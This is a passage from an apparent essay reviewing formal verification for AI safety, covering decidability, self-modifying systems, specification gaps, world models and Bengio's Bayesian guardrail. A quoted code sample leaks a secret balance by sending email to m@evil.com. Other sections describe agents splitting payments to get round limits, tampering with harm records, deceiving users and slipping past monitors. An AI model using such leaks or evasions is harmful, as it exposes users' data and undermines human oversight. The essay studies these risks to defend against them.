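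A single pass through a neural network always stops, because it is a fixed number of additions, multiplications and similar operations. If the input has $L$ bits, a program could try all $2^L$ possible inputs and check every output. The same is true of a language model with a limited context and finite-precision numbers, so its safety is decidable in principle, given a rule that a program can apply to each output. In practice nobody could finish the search, since even a black-and-white image of 28 by 28 pixels has about $10^{236}$ possible versions. The obstacle to verifying a fixed network is therefore the amount of computation required, as the previous section described, rather than undecidability.

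An agent is harder because it runs the model in a loop. An earlier version of the paper, *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment* (2024), explains that the loop can run forever even if software cuts off each of the model's answers at a fixed length. It suggests adding a counter that forces the whole system into a final state after a set number of steps.

The title of the 2025 paper claims too much for halting. This program halts on every input:

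```
check(n):
    if n is even, above 2 and not the sum of two primes:  open the safe
```

But it is safe on every input only if Goldbach's conjecture is true. Limiting the input size makes the question decidable here. A program also doesn't have to halt to be proved safe. The £100 payment wrapper can run forever, and a short proof by induction still shows that it never exceeds its limit.

Melo and colleagues acknowledge that checking every input is intractable, and they say in the earlier version that halting alone doesn't make an AI aligned. They also describe a more practical approach, a gatekeeper that applies a "judge function" to each output and substitutes a harmless default for any output the function rejects. They say the main difficulty is defining the judge function.

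### Systems that rewrite themselves

A safety certificate for an AI may no longer apply after the AI changes its own code. Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, argues that this rules out lasting certificates for any truly general AI. He replies to Melo and colleagues that checking one finite system is decidable, though it sometimes takes an infeasible amount of computation, but no algorithm can decide whether a rule holds for all possible finite systems. He argues that a self-modifying AI needs this wider guarantee because it could become any of those systems.

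His main theorem concerns a rewriting procedure $\Phi$, which turns the program $x$ into its next version, $\Phi(x)$. No algorithm can decide, for every $x$, whether

$$x \text{ is safe} \iff \Phi(x) \text{ is safe}$$

The proof applies Rice's theorem to the property "rewriting leaves this program's safety unchanged". It makes these assumptions:

- The rewriting procedure can be any computable one, but what the new version does must depend only on what the old version did, not on how somebody wrote the code.
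- A program that never produces any output counts as unsafe, and its next version is unsafe too.
- At least one safe program becomes unsafe when rewritten.

A program that does nothing will never open the safe, so it is odd to count it as unsafe. This matters little, because the same proof, with small changes, works for prohibitions.

The larger problem is Gumbau Mezquita's conclusion that no algorithm can tell whether the next version of a system will be safe, even if we know the current one is. He infers that only a system that has stopped changing can have a lasting certificate. His own example contradicts this. In it, a program is "safe" if it answers every input, and rewriting removes every answer except the one to input 0. The example meets all the theorem's assumptions, yet if we know the current version is safe, we also know the next one won't be. The undecidable question in this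 example is whether the current version is safe.

The conclusion is true of some rewriting procedures. For example, a procedure could take a puzzle stored in the current version and produce a new version that solves the puzzle and then opens the safe. But nobody has to let an AI rewrite itself like that. The £100 limit on an AI behind the payment wrapper will hold however often the AI rewrites itself, as long as it can't alter or bypass the wrapper.

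Gumbau Mezquita also proves that a changing system can fool any practical verifier indefinitely. However, he defines a practical verifier as one that checks behaviour only on a finite set of inputs, which makes it a test, whereas a proof about the code can cover infinitely many inputs. He discusses restricted rewriting and proof-carrying code as ways to contain an AI, but thinks they sacrifice generality or speed.

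Moser, Frolov and colleagues (2026) describe the trade-off more clearly in *The Self-Improvement Problem*. They consider a gate that approves or rejects updates to an AI, and prove that no such gate can approve every improvement and reject everything else. Their proof, which they checked in Lean, constructs an update that is good if the gate rejects it and bad if the gate approves it. The result holds even if the gate can make random choices and is allowed to be wrong up to a third of the time.

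A builder can drop the requirement to approve every improvement. The Gödel machine, Jürgen Schmidhuber's design for a self-improving program, rewrites itself only when it has proved that the change is useful. If no proof can settle whether a change would help, the machine will "simply ignore it", according to *Goedel Machines*.

Moser and colleagues also show that a gate can reliably find improvements if it evaluates a limited number of updates using a score it can compute in limited time. But they construct a series of updates in which each one raises the measured score and lowers the true score. For example, each update might fix one task in the test set and break two outside it. This result is more relevant to current practice than the impossibility theorem, because developers choose between versions by their test scores.

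### The cost of refusing without a proof

A builder who insists on proofs will reject some safe programs. How many depends on the programs and on how good the proof methods are. Among all 483,641 valid programs of up to four instructions in a small test language, Pérez-Acle's methods certified 98.2% for the rule about the safe, with no mistakes. Cruder methods reject more safe programs. In a separate set of simple finite models, he approved only those that contained no forbidden operation, which admitted 71.9% of the safe models with three states and 47.3% of those with five. None of these figures measures the share of useful AI-written software that a gatekeeper would refuse.

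Some of the gatekeeper's refusals are temporary. A program that opened the safe if it found a counterexample to the Riemann hypothesis, a conjecture about prime numbers, would have had no certificate for most of 2026. By 20 November, mathematicians were racing to verify an AI proof of the hypothesis and a human proof had emerged, according to Quanta Magazine's *Transformation*. Once somebody translates a proof into a form that the gatekeeper's checker accepts, the gatekeeper can admit the program.

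The builder can also change the program, for example by adding a guard that stops it whenever it is about to open the safe. If the original was safe, the guard never acts and the program behaves as before, but its safety now has a very short proof. The theorems don't exclude this, because Pérez-Acle's gatekeeper has to admit or refuse each program unaltered. Similarly, in the case of the secret memos, the builder can give a dummy memo to the part of the program that writes the report. If the report never depended on the secret, it will come out the same.

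The duty to answer every customer has no such general repair. A programmer could set a deadline and send a default answer when it passes, but some customers would then get the default instead of the real answer they would eventually have received.

When a safety rule prohibits an act, undecidability need not force a builder to rule out any safe behaviour if software can recognise the act just before it happens. It is easy to recognise an attempt to open a safe or make a payment over £100. It is much harder to recognise an email that manipulates its reader, or to judge a DNA sequence whose effects nobody understands.

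## Which safety failures can be written as formal properties

A proof rules out only the failures defined in its specification, and some failures are much easier to define exactly than others. The table lists them from easiest to hardest to express as formal properties.

| Failure | Candidate formal property | What could still happen |
|---|---|---|
| An agent takes a forbidden action | The agent deletes files only in the scratch folder | The agent overwrites a contract with blank text |
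| An output has a forbidden form | No response contains "tulip47" | The model writes "tulip forty-seven" |
| A secret leaks | Public outputs have the same probabilities whatever the secret is | The agent reveals something that nobody labelled secret |
| A model deceives or manipulates someone | The model never intentionally causes a false belief that it does not share | The model misleads someone in a way the definitions of "belief" and "intention" do not capture |
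| A model has a harmful aim | The model would behave the same way if its actions no longer served that aim | The model has an aim that nobody thought to list |

### Actions and strings

Moon and Varshney include network access, irreversible payments, the destruction of files and tampering with monitoring software among the failures that a containment layer can exclude. If $e$ is the event at some step and $f$ is a file, the rule about deletions is

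$$e = \text{delete}(f) \;\Rightarrow\; f \in \text{Scratch} \qquad \text{at every step}$$

A rule that forbids only deletion still allows overwriting a contract, which destroys it. But the designer can check each event type in the interface's list to see whether it could destroy a file.

Rules about the form of an output can use constrained decoding. Before the model writes each token, software checks which tokens would break the rule and sets their probabilities to zero, as *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (2026) explains. It then scales up the others so that they add up to 1. If $s$ is the text so far and $V(s)$ is the set of permitted tokens, the new probability of a permitted token $t$ is

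$$p'(t \mid s) = \frac{p(t \mid s)}{\sum_{u \in V(s)} p(u \mid s)}$$

This method makes a response impossible, whereas RLHF can make it extremely unlikely. The software also has to keep the model from reaching a dead end, so the monitor described in *ChopChop* (2025) checks whether the text so far can still become something the rule permits.

Suppose the rule bans the password "tulip47", and the model has written "The password is tulip". The model then gives "47" a probability of 0.9 of coming next, a full stop 0.06 and "forty" 0.04. Blocking "47" raises the full stop to 0.6 and "forty" to 0.4. The exact password can no longer appear, but the model is ten times as likely to start writing it as "tulip forty-seven".

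Constrained decoding works better for an agent's requests to software, where it can guarantee that each request has a format the containment layer accepts. *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata* (2026) offers such a guarantee for diffusion models, another type of language model, but warns that a correctly formed request can still be malicious.

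### Leaks

A ban on one string misses paraphrases because it concerns the text and not the information in it. Noninterference, a standard idea in computer security, addresses the information directly. For any two possible secrets $s_1$ and $s_2$ and any public output $o$, it requires

$$P(o \mid s_1) = P(o \mid s_2)$$

Someone who sees only the public output then learns nothing about the secret, even if the agent writes in code.

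To enforce this, software can make a "secret" label follow the data, as Tether does with files. This is easy to get wrong. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe a leak in CaMeL, the information-flow tool mentioned earlier, that works like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
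```

If the secret balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The next line does nothing, so `rich` stays true without a label and the software allows the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the customer is rich.

Garby and colleagues designed a programming language for agents that prevents such leaks. They proved in Lean that a form of noninterference holds for every program written in it, including agents that write and run their own code. On a banking benchmark, their agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

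The theorem still allows a secret to affect whether a program finishes. Garby and colleagues bound how much this can reveal. If a program fails to finish 2% of the time with either of two secrets, the probability of any public result can differ between them by at most 2 percentage points. But small leaks can add up over repeated runs. CaMeL ran inside an ordinary retry loop that nobody had labelled, and an attacker could use the retries to extract a whole secret one bit at a time.

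Strict noninterference also forbids useful behaviour, so programmers need a way to relabel data. For example, if an agent sorts a stranger's email into one of a few categories, a programmer might decide to trust the category but not the email. The theorem proves a limit on what this decision can affect, but not that the decision was wise.

### Deception, flattery and manipulation

Deception has formal definitions. In *Experiments with Detecting and Mitigating AI Deception* (2023), one agent deceives another about a claim if it intentionally causes the other's decision, the other has a false belief about the claim, and the deceiver does not believe the claim. The paper defines belief by behaviour. An agent believes a claim if it acts as though it had observed that the claim was true, and would have acted differently if it had observed that the claim was false.

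Under the definition in *AI Deception* (2025), a system deceives if its signals systematically cause false beliefs that change other people's actions in the system's favour, whether or not the system intends to deceive.

Suppose a sales assistant wrongly tells customers that a warranty covers water damage, and they buy the product. If the assistant acts in every way as though the claim were true, it has not deceived anyone under the first definition, but it may have under the second. *From Deceptive Outputs to Deceptive Mechanisms* (2026) adds that a model may repeat a falsehood because its training made that sentence likely, or because the sentence will mislead the listener. A transcript could look the same in both cases.

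The definitions work in small mathematical games, where the designer specifies what each player knows and wants. To apply them to the sales assistant, someone would need a similar model of every customer, including what each would have done with accurate information.

Manipulation is even harder to write as a formal property. *Evaluating Language Models for Harmful Manipulation* (2026) defines it as influencing people's decisions by deliberately bypassing or weakening their ability to reason. The *International AI Safety Report 2026* notes that researchers disagree about how to distinguish it from legitimate influence.

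Some narrower properties are easier to state. To limit flattery, a designer could require a model to give an essay the same distribution of grades whether or not the user claims to have written it. This is a noninterference property in which the user's claim of authorship is the secret input. But a model that praised every essay would also satisfy it, so the property covers only one kind of flattery.

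### Aims inside the model

The 2023 paper on deception also describes an agent as a system that would adapt its behaviour if its actions affected the world differently. This suggests a way to state that a model lacks a particular aim. For example, a payment agent that splits large transfers into small ones to get round a limit should stop when the limit no longer applies, while one that is copying a habit from its training examples should carry on.

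A formal version would require the agent's behaviour to stay the same in a world where splitting transfers achieves nothing. But someone has to think of the aim first and choose the right alternative world. This test could also miss an aim that the agent could pursue only with much more power, because that aim might not affect how it pays bills. A theorem about the weights could avoid relying on behaviour, but researchers would first have to define which patterns in the weights amount to an aim.

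### Vacuous, mistaken and incomplete specifications

Even when a property is easy to express, its specification can fail by being vacuous, meaning that it holds without restricting anything that matters. *KaPilot* (2026) gives the simplest case, a specification that requires a program to behave correctly only when "false" is true. Every program passes because that condition never arises. *Bounded Loops* (2026) traces the modern idea of vacuity to a 2001 paper by Beer and others, and notes that commercial verification tools now routinely check for it.

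Contradictory assumptions have the same effect, because anything follows from a contradiction. *Beyond LLM Judge* (2026) describes a formal statement about mathematical functions that passed a faithfulness check even though two of its assumptions contradicted each other. The project now replaces each theorem's conclusion with a meaningless placeholder. If the original proof still works, it never depended on the conclusion, and the assumptions are probably contradictory.

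A specification may also state a real property that is weaker than the intended one. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) give the example of a program that should return the largest number in a list. If the specification requires only that the result is not negative, a program that always returns 0 passes, even for the list 5, 3, 7. When they reran an earlier method for producing verified code, the Dafny verifier accepted 99.1% of the programs on one benchmark, but 94.7% of those came with no statement of what the result should be. The method did not require one, so Dafny had mostly checked other properties, such as whether the programs would finish.

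Other specifications omit a necessary requirement. A company might want a program that removes duplicate customers from a database, and require only that no customer appears twice afterwards. A program that deletes every customer meets this requirement, because the company didn't also require that each original customer remain in the database.

The £100 limit could go wrong in a similar way. Suppose the company starts buying from abroad, and a programmer adds a currency to each payment request. The wrapper still adds the bare amounts to $T$, and the proof that $T \le 100$ still works. But the agent can now pay 100 Kuwaiti dinars, worth more than £200, and the wrapper will record 100. The company meant

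$$\sum_i a_i \cdot \text{rate}(c_i) \le 100$$

where $a_i$ is the amount of payment $i$, $c_i$ is its currency, and $\text{rate}(c_i)$ is the value of one unit in pounds. This is no harder to prove. But exchange rates come from outside the software, so the company now has to trust whoever supplies them.

### Ethical principles as code

In October 2026, Drechsler and Plump proposed writing selected ethical principles as formal properties and using them throughout an AI's development, an approach they call Formal Raising. Each principle has a priority and a test for whether an action violates it. In their example, protection of life has priority 100, truthfulness 50 and privacy 40. The designer can also mark a principle as strict.

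Drechsler and Plump's program compares possible actions against principles ranked by priority. Starting from the highest priority, it prefers the action with fewer violations at the first level where they differ. Suppose an attacker asks where someone is. Telling the truth would endanger a life, and protecting life ranks above truthfulness, so the program chooses to lie without needing a specific exception for attackers. If two actions have the same violations at every level, the program reports that it can't decide. Drechsler and Plump suggest turning its verdicts into training examples and using the undecided cases to find gaps in the principles.

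This makes moral priorities explicit, but it doesn't turn most of them into invariants. The program will lie whenever the alternatives are worse. Even a strict rule is guaranteed to hold only if a permitted action, such as doing nothing, is always available. The result also depends on which actions the AI proposes. Here it didn't propose refusing to answer the attacker, which might have violated neither principle.

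The example appears to contain a specification error. It marks non-discrimination, but not protection of life, as strict, so the program would endanger a life rather than discriminate. Drechsler and Plump say their priorities are only illustrative. Still, anyone can find this problem by reading a few lines of code, which is an advantage over a principle encoded in a network's weights.

The main limitation is the program's input, which consists of yes-or-no values for questions such as whether an action is a deliberate lie. In one example, the program ranks an assistant that presents the facts above one that uses misleading emotional pressure, but only because the input already classifies the pressure as manipulative. The program shows how to combine moral judgements that someone has already made, but it doesn't make manipulation easier to recognise in a real conversation. Drechsler and Plump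 acknowledge that a wrong classification can make a formally correct decision inappropriate. They have demonstrated the reasoning on small scenarios and have not yet trained a model this way.

### From English to a formal language

A rule usually starts in ordinary language, and a person or an AI then has to translate it into a formal property. No program can fully check the translation, because ordinary language has no formal definition to compare it with, as *Symbolic Informalization* (2026) points out. A rule may also have several faithful translations, a problem that *Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* (2026) distinguishes from mistranslation. In "Spend at most £100 a day", for example, "a day" could mean a calendar day or any 24-hour period.

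Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier-Stokes lost in translation*, studied mismatches between mathematical texts and their Lean versions. They accept that Lean shows the formal theorems to be correct, but ask whether the text and the Lean version make the same argument.

In one test, GPT-6 Astra was given a true statement about $x^3 - x^2 - x + 1$ with a faulty proof, which factorised the expression as $(x-1)(x+1)^2$, and was asked to write the same argument in Lean. The model returned a valid proof that used the correct factors, $(x-1)^2(x+1)$, so Lean had checked a different argument from the one in the text. There are subtler differences between the written and Lean versions of OpenAI's proof that solutions to the Navier-Stokes equations, which describe fluid flow, can blow up in finite time. One estimate in the written paper needs four extra derivatives of a function, while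 the closest Lean version needs five.

Neither mismatch would matter to a gatekeeper, which relies on the formal theorem, not a written explanation of it, but a mismatch in the theorem's statement or definitions would matter a great deal. Bastounis and colleagues show how one can arise. Let $n$ be the smallest natural number for which $x + y = n$ has no solution in natural numbers, and let $r = 1/(n+1)$. The equation always has the solution $x = n$, $y = 0$, so no such $n$ exists and $r$ is undefined. But Lean's standard function for finding the smallest member of a set of natural numbers returns 0 if the set is empty. A translation that uses this function sets $n = 0$ and $r = 1$, and Lean correctly proves that $(r+1)^2 = r^2 + 2r + 1$.

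The same thing could happen with a safety rule. Suppose a machine must stop unless its highest temperature reading is below 80 degrees, and the software sets the highest reading to 0 when there are no readings. If every sensor were disconnected, the machine would keep running without breaking the rule.

Bastounis and colleagues also prove that no program can always tell whether any number fits a definition like the one for $n$. For any program, mathematicians can construct an equation that has a solution for a given $n$ exactly when the program stops on input $n$. So a smallest $n$ without a solution exists exactly when the program runs forever on some input. Deciding this for every program would be impossible even if we could always tell whether a program stops on a given input, because there are infinitely many inputs to check.

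The paper concludes that faithful translation is harder than any computational problem in the hierarchy it uses. But this result applies to a translator that must either translate or correctly reject every text. Like a gatekeeper, a translator can avoid this limit by rejecting any definition it can't prove meaningful, though it will then reject some good ones.

Bastounis and colleagues describe a project in which Meta claimed to have translated 26 mathematics textbooks into Lean. Meta reported formalising 56% of the target statements in one book, but a Lean user who checked the formalised statements could not find one without a fatal error.

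Translators also tend to repair mistakes without mentioning them. In *FaithformBench*, Cornish, Ghinassi and colleagues (2026) took 12,784 steps from correct mathematical arguments, introduced errors and had eight AI systems translate them. One altered step was "if $3^x = 5$, then $3^{x+2} = 51$" (the correct value is 45). One system changed $x$ from a real number to a natural number. No natural number satisfies $3^x = 5$, so the false claim became vacuously true. Among the specialised systems, the one best at translating correct steps was also, on the harder problems, the most likely to make wrong steps provable. General-purpose models, including Claude Opus 4.7, did this less often.

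*LeanSide* (2026) reports a similar pattern in students' proofs. Experts judged that the translation software had misrepresented 18 of 1,038 correct steps and 22 of 117 incorrect ones. Someone who states a mistaken safety rule could likewise receive a proof of a different rule, with no warning that the software had changed the original.

### Why an incomplete specification may be enough

*Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) describes a range of ways to specify a program, from a few tests that settle likely misunderstandings to a full specification. A rule that stops an agent from deleting backups prevents a serious harm even if nobody defines deception. Moon and Varshney argue that the most serious agent failures involve an action at a software boundary. Many do, but an AI that can persuade an administrator to delete the backups can cause the same harm without breaking the rule.

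People can also read a short specification. A reviewer could spot the missing currency in one line, whereas nobody could find a comparable mistake by reading a network's weights. This advantage shrinks when a short rule depends on long definitions. For example, "The sequence is not toxic" is five words, but the definition of "toxic" could be extremely long. Ammann points out that specifications also contain choices about acceptable risk, so the people affected should have a say.

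AI can help by looking for counterexamples, which are cases that meet the specification but that people would reject, such as the payment of 100 dinars. Like a proof, a counterexample is useful even if nobody trusts the AI that found it, because a person can judge the case themselves. *VerusEval* (2026) tests whether specifications accept correct outputs and reject wrong outputs and invalid inputs.

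Testing a specification on concrete cases works better than asking an AI whether it is correct. In *Verus-SpecGym* (2026), test cases exposed faults in 191 AI-written specifications, but an AI judge approved 49 of them. However, finding no faults doesn't prove that a specification has no gaps, and a more capable AI might find one that the tests missed.

### The reward model as a specification

The reward model in RLHF is also a specification, but it is learned and implicit. Like a formal specification, it can differ from what people want, but the two tend to fail differently. A formal specification permits anything it doesn't exclude, so the rule $T \le 100$ allows a rude email. A reward model gives the email a score even if its designers never thought about rudeness, and that score may well be sensible. But if raters tend to prefer answers that agree with them, the reward model can learn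 to reward flattery. Developers have to discover this by testing examples, because it isn't written in any line of code.

Designers could combine the two by putting a learned judge inside a formal rule, such as "never send an email that the manipulation detector scores above 0.5". A containment layer could provably enforce this rule for every email. But the proof would cover only the detector's scores, so an agent could still send a manipulative email that scored 0.4. The guarantee about manipulation would depend on the detector's training, much as RLHF depends on the reward model's.

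### A contest between specifications and training

The dispute is partly about whether people can write specifications without serious gaps, and a contest could test this. Several teams would write formal rules for the same agent, such as one that handles a company's invoices and customer emails. Other teams would use the best available AI to look for harmful sequences of actions that the rules allow, and would win a prize for each one they found. The first teams would then repair their rules, and the contest would continue.

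If the attackers were soon finding only trivial problems, this would be good evidence that people can audit specifications for such work. If they kept finding serious ones, proofs about these agents would often guarantee the wrong thing. The organisers should also run the contest on an agent with behavioural training but no formal rules, and on one with both. They would learn which harms each method prevents, and whether the formal rules add enough to justify the work they block.

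Researchers could test formal definitions of deception and manipulation against people's judgements of new conversations. A definition that agreed with those judgements as closely as people agree with each other would be a major advance, especially if it still did so after an AI had searched for ways around it.

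## Whether a proof about a model holds in the physical world

Even if a specification matches exactly what people want and the proof is correct, the system can still violate the specification if the mathematical model of the machine or its surroundings is wrong. For ordinary software, the model can be nearly exact, because the program's text determines what it does on working hardware. Nobody has a comparably exact model of a virus in a human body. The value of a proof about physical harm therefore depends on how far reality can differ from the model and whether anyone would notice in time.

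### Dickson's objections

Andrew Dickson argued in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) that formal verification is very unlikely to give strong guarantees against the major AI threats in the near term.

Dickson first argued that proofs concern symbols, not the physical world. Engineers at NASA's Jet Propulsion Laboratory used a verification tool on the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021. The guarantee covered flaws in the software, but not a failed landing or even a short circuit in the computer. By Dickson's figures, about half of all Mars missions have failed, and software accounts for about a fifth of the risk, so perfect software would have cut the failure rate only from about 50% to about 40%.

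Scientists also lack detailed models of the things people most fear. Dickson's main example was Tegmark and Omohundro's proof-checking DNA synthesiser. He argued that predicting precisely what a new virus would do to a person would require simulating the virus and the whole body over several years. In 2022, a leading simulation covered one very simple cell for 20 minutes of simulated time, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells. Society is no easier to model, because whether a chatbot's answer misinforms anyone depends on who reads it and what they do with it.

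A simulation also needs a starting state, and Dickson doubted that anyone could measure one accurately enough. In 2024, Google researchers finished mapping about a millionth of a human brain, which produced 1.4 petabytes of data. At that rate, a whole brain would take about 1.4 million petabytes.

Dickson said that engineers' figures for how likely a bridge or a drone is to fail are estimates, not guarantees, and mostly come from past results. An estimate may be good enough for a bridge, but it is much less reassuring for a DNA synthesiser, because an attacker with a 1% chance of getting a dangerous pathogen can keep trying.

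### Bounds in place of predictions

Nora Ammann replied to Dickson and other critics in *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* (2025). She accepted that no model is a perfect copy of the world, but argued that a safety proof needs only a bound, not an exact prediction. A model can be right that a temperature will stay below 50 degrees without predicting its exact value. She called such a model a sound overapproximation, meaning that it allows everything that can really happen, and perhaps some things that can't.

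Suppose an AI controls the heater in a chemical tank that must never get hotter than 50°C. The heater can add up to 2 degrees a minute, and the room is never above 25°C. Each minute, the tank loses heat in proportion to the difference between its temperature $T$ and the room's temperature $R$:

$$\frac{dT}{dt} = u - 0.1\,(T - R), \qquad 0 \le u \le 2, \quad R \le 25$$

The AI chooses the heating rate $u$. At 50 degrees, full heating in the hottest room gives $2 - 0.1 \times 25 = -0.5$, so the tank is cooling. A tank that starts below 50 degrees can therefore never pass 50, whatever the AI does. The proof requires no simulation of the tank, and its only assumption about the starting temperature is that it was below 50. Dickson's point about initial conditions is therefore weak for systems like this.

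Dalrymple and colleagues suggest that the model should similarly list everything a person might do, without probabilities, and that the proof should cover every case. A self-driving car would have to be safe whether a pedestrian waited or stepped into the road. But people can do so many things that a complete list might leave the car unable to move.

Chaotic systems are also hard to bound, because small errors grow quickly. If an error doubles every day, a millimetre becomes about 1,000 kilometres in 30 days. Ammann replies that the approach suits areas with solid science and little chaos, but not chatbots or problems that depend on what particular individuals do. Ammann thus concedes much of what Dickson said about misinformation.

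### Three claims about a DNA synthesiser

Dickson and his critics were partly arguing about different claims.

| Claim to prove | What the model must describe | What could still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| The machine makes only sequences on an approved list | The machine and its software | Someone joins approved pieces into a dangerous sequence |
| A virus with this sequence cannot enter a human cell | How the virus interacts with the surface of human cells | The sequence does harm in another way, such as by coding for a toxin |
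| The sequence will not harm anyone | Human bodies, and everything people might do with the sequence | Anything the model leaves out |

Dickson was mainly attacking the claim in the last row. In a comment on Ammann's reply, Omohundro said that he and Tegmark had meant something like the claim in the first row. A biosafety board would decide which sequences were safe, and the machine would provably refuse all others. This target is much more realistic, but it leaves the board to judge the biology. It is also narrower than an example in the guaranteed safe AI paper by Dalrymple and colleagues, including Omohundro, in which an AI verifies whether a sequence's risk stays below a set limit.

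Ammann defended the claim about cell entry. Software would model how each protein the virus codes for interacts with each protein on the surface of human cells, in a tiny patch of cell membrane. If no pair could let the virus in, the virus could not infect anyone. The method would also reject some useful gene therapies, which have to enter cells to work. Ammann said her wider plan for defending against viruses this way was too hard for current technology.

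Using a simplified model would take far less computation than simulating a body, but the simplification has to be right. Influenza viruses attach to a sugar called sialic acid on the surface of cells. If a model included the surface proteins but left out their sugars, a valid proof based on it could lead to the false conclusion that flu cannot infect people.

Dickson raised another problem that affects all three claims. A buyer has to know that the physical machine is the one the proof describes, with no hidden changes or manufacturing defects. In response, Ammann proposed using cryptography to tie each proof to a particular device. This works only if the device resists tampering, and Tegmark and Omohundro still list tamper resistance as an open problem.

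### How model error limits a guarantee

Let $W$ be the event that the model is wrong, meaning that the world does something the model excludes. At worst, a wrong model makes harm certain, so

$$P(\text{harm}) \;\le\; P(W) + P(\text{harm} \mid \text{not } W)$$

A proof can bound only the last term. If it proves a bound of one in a million, and there is a 1% chance that the model is wrong, the total bound is 1.0001%. A proof that reduced the last term to zero would lower the total bound only to 1%. Halving the chance that the model is wrong would almost halve the total bound.

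The 1% has to come from measurements, experience and expert judgement, not from a proof checker, so Dickson is right that a physical guarantee always includes an estimate. This supports Hatfield-Dodds's objection that a world model only moves the problem.

The estimate matters even more over long periods. Dalrymple and colleagues note that if the model has at most a chance $\epsilon$ of being wrong at each step, a plan proved safe will stay safe for $n$ steps with probability at least $(1-\epsilon)^n$. If $\epsilon$ is one in 10,000 per hour, the lower bound for a year is only 42%. To raise it to 99%, $\epsilon$ would have to be about one in 870,000 per hour.

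These are worst-case figures, because a wrong model does not always lead to harm. Suppose dirt on the tank reduces its heat loss by 30%, so that the 0.1 in the equation becomes 0.07. Full heating in a 25-degree room would then heat the tank to nearly 54 degrees. But according to the original model, a tank that starts below 45 degrees can never rise above 45. A reading of 46 would therefore reveal the error while there was still time to turn off the heater. If a monitor like this caught 99% of model errors in time, the 1% in the bound would fall to 0.01%.

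Ammann's reply also describes a design in which the AI stays in control only while a simpler backup controller could still return the system to safety. The proof then has to cover only the next few steps.

In a comment, Hatfield-Dodds called monitoring an excellent idea but said it would be pointless for anyone who believed they had a guarantee. This is a reasonable complaint about the word "guarantee", but a proof and monitoring can still be used together, because monitoring watches for events that the model excludes and the proof therefore doesn't cover.

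Monitoring works only if there is time to react and a safe action to take. For example, an operator can switch off a heater but can't recall a virus after its release. Attackers also look for cases that the model gets wrong, so the error rate under attack could be much higher than the rate measured in normal operation.

Dalrymple and colleagues offer two general defences of world models. The first is that every approach to AI safety makes assumptions about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit. This is a good reason to prefer world models, but it doesn't show that their assumptions are true. The second is that an AI able to carry out complicated, dangerous plans reliably would itself need to predict the world well, so sufficiently accurate models must be possible. That seems too optimistic, because an attacker needs to predict the results of only one plan, while a defender's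 model has to cover every plan. The AI's knowledge might also be stored in weights that nobody can audit.

### A guardrail that considers many theories

A gatekeeper could use many models of the world instead of relying on one. Yoshua Bengio, who also co-wrote the guaranteed safe AI paper, studied this approach with Cohen and colleagues in *Can a Bayesian Oracle Prevent Harm from an Agent?* (2024). They asked how software could limit the chance of harm if it had many theories of the world and it was unclear which was true.

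Each theory starts with a prior probability. As data arrive, the software updates it to a posterior probability, which is proportional to the prior multiplied by how likely the theory made the data. Before the agent acts, the guardrail calculates the chance of harm under each theory. For example:

| Theory | Posterior probability | Chance that the action causes harm |
|---|---|---|
| A | 90% | 0.1% |
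| B | 8% | 20% |
| C | 2% | 90% |

The weighted average is about 3.5%, so a guardrail with a 5% limit on the average would allow the action. But if B or C is true, the action is very dangerous. The guardrail could instead use the most pessimistic theory, but it would then refuse almost everything, because some far-fetched theory usually predicts disaster.

Bengio and colleagues use the most pessimistic *plausible* theory. They rank the theories by posterior probability and keep each theory whose probability is at least $\alpha$ times the combined probability of that theory and those ranked above it. With $\alpha = 0.05$, the guardrail keeps A and B and puts the chance of harm at 20%. With $\alpha = 0.01$, it also keeps C and puts the chance at 90%.

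Write $p^*$ for the prior probability of the true theory. The theorem says that if $\alpha < \delta p^*$, then with a probability of at least $1-\delta$, the guardrail never underestimates the true chance of harm. The proof has two steps:

- The true theory generated the data, so the data are unlikely to count heavily against it. With a probability of at least $1-\delta$, its posterior never falls below $\delta p^*$.
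- This is more than $\alpha$, and the combined probability of any group of theories is at most 1. The guardrail therefore always keeps the true theory, and the highest estimate among the theories it keeps is at least as high as the true one.

The observations don't have to be independent, which matters because an agent's actions affect what it sees next. But the true theory must be among those considered. If it isn't, its prior is zero and no $\alpha$ is small enough. More data can't help, because updating only moves probability between the theories being considered. Even if the true theory is among them, nobody knows which one it is, so nobody can be sure how small $\alpha$ has to be.

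The researchers tested the idea in a simple game. An agent repeatedly chose between ten options, and any reward above a certain level caused an explosion that ended the game. There were 1,024 theories about the rewards, all equally likely at first, and one was always true. Being 99% sure of never underestimating the risk would require an $\alpha$ below about one in 100,000. The guardrail blocked almost every action when $\alpha$ was near zero. It rarely blocked any when $\alpha$ was near one, and the agent often caused an explosion. At values in between, it did about as well as a guardrail that used the average, so the extra caution had no clear benefit even when the theorem's main assumption held.

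The guardrail also learns from records of harm, which an agent might tamper with. As long as the records are accurate, no data can distinguish the theory "this causes harm" from the theory "this causes a record of harm". With a small enough $\alpha$, the guardrail is likely to keep both theories, so it could refuse the first attempt at tampering if tampering is harm under the true theory.

### Scientist AI

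Bengio has since developed this work into a proposal called Scientist AI at LawZero, the research organisation he founded. *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor* (Bengio, Richardson and colleagues, 2026) describes a neural network, the Predictor, that estimates the probability that statements are true. Its training data separate facts from claims, so a web page saying that the Earth is flat becomes "someone wrote that the Earth is flat". Training never rewards the Predictor for what happens after people use its predictions. The researchers argue that it is therefore unlikely to develop goals of its own, and that a guardrail could use it to estimate the harm an agent's action might cause.

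Their main theorem bounds the chance that training produces a dangerous Predictor:

$$P(\text{dangerous Predictor}) \le C \times R$$

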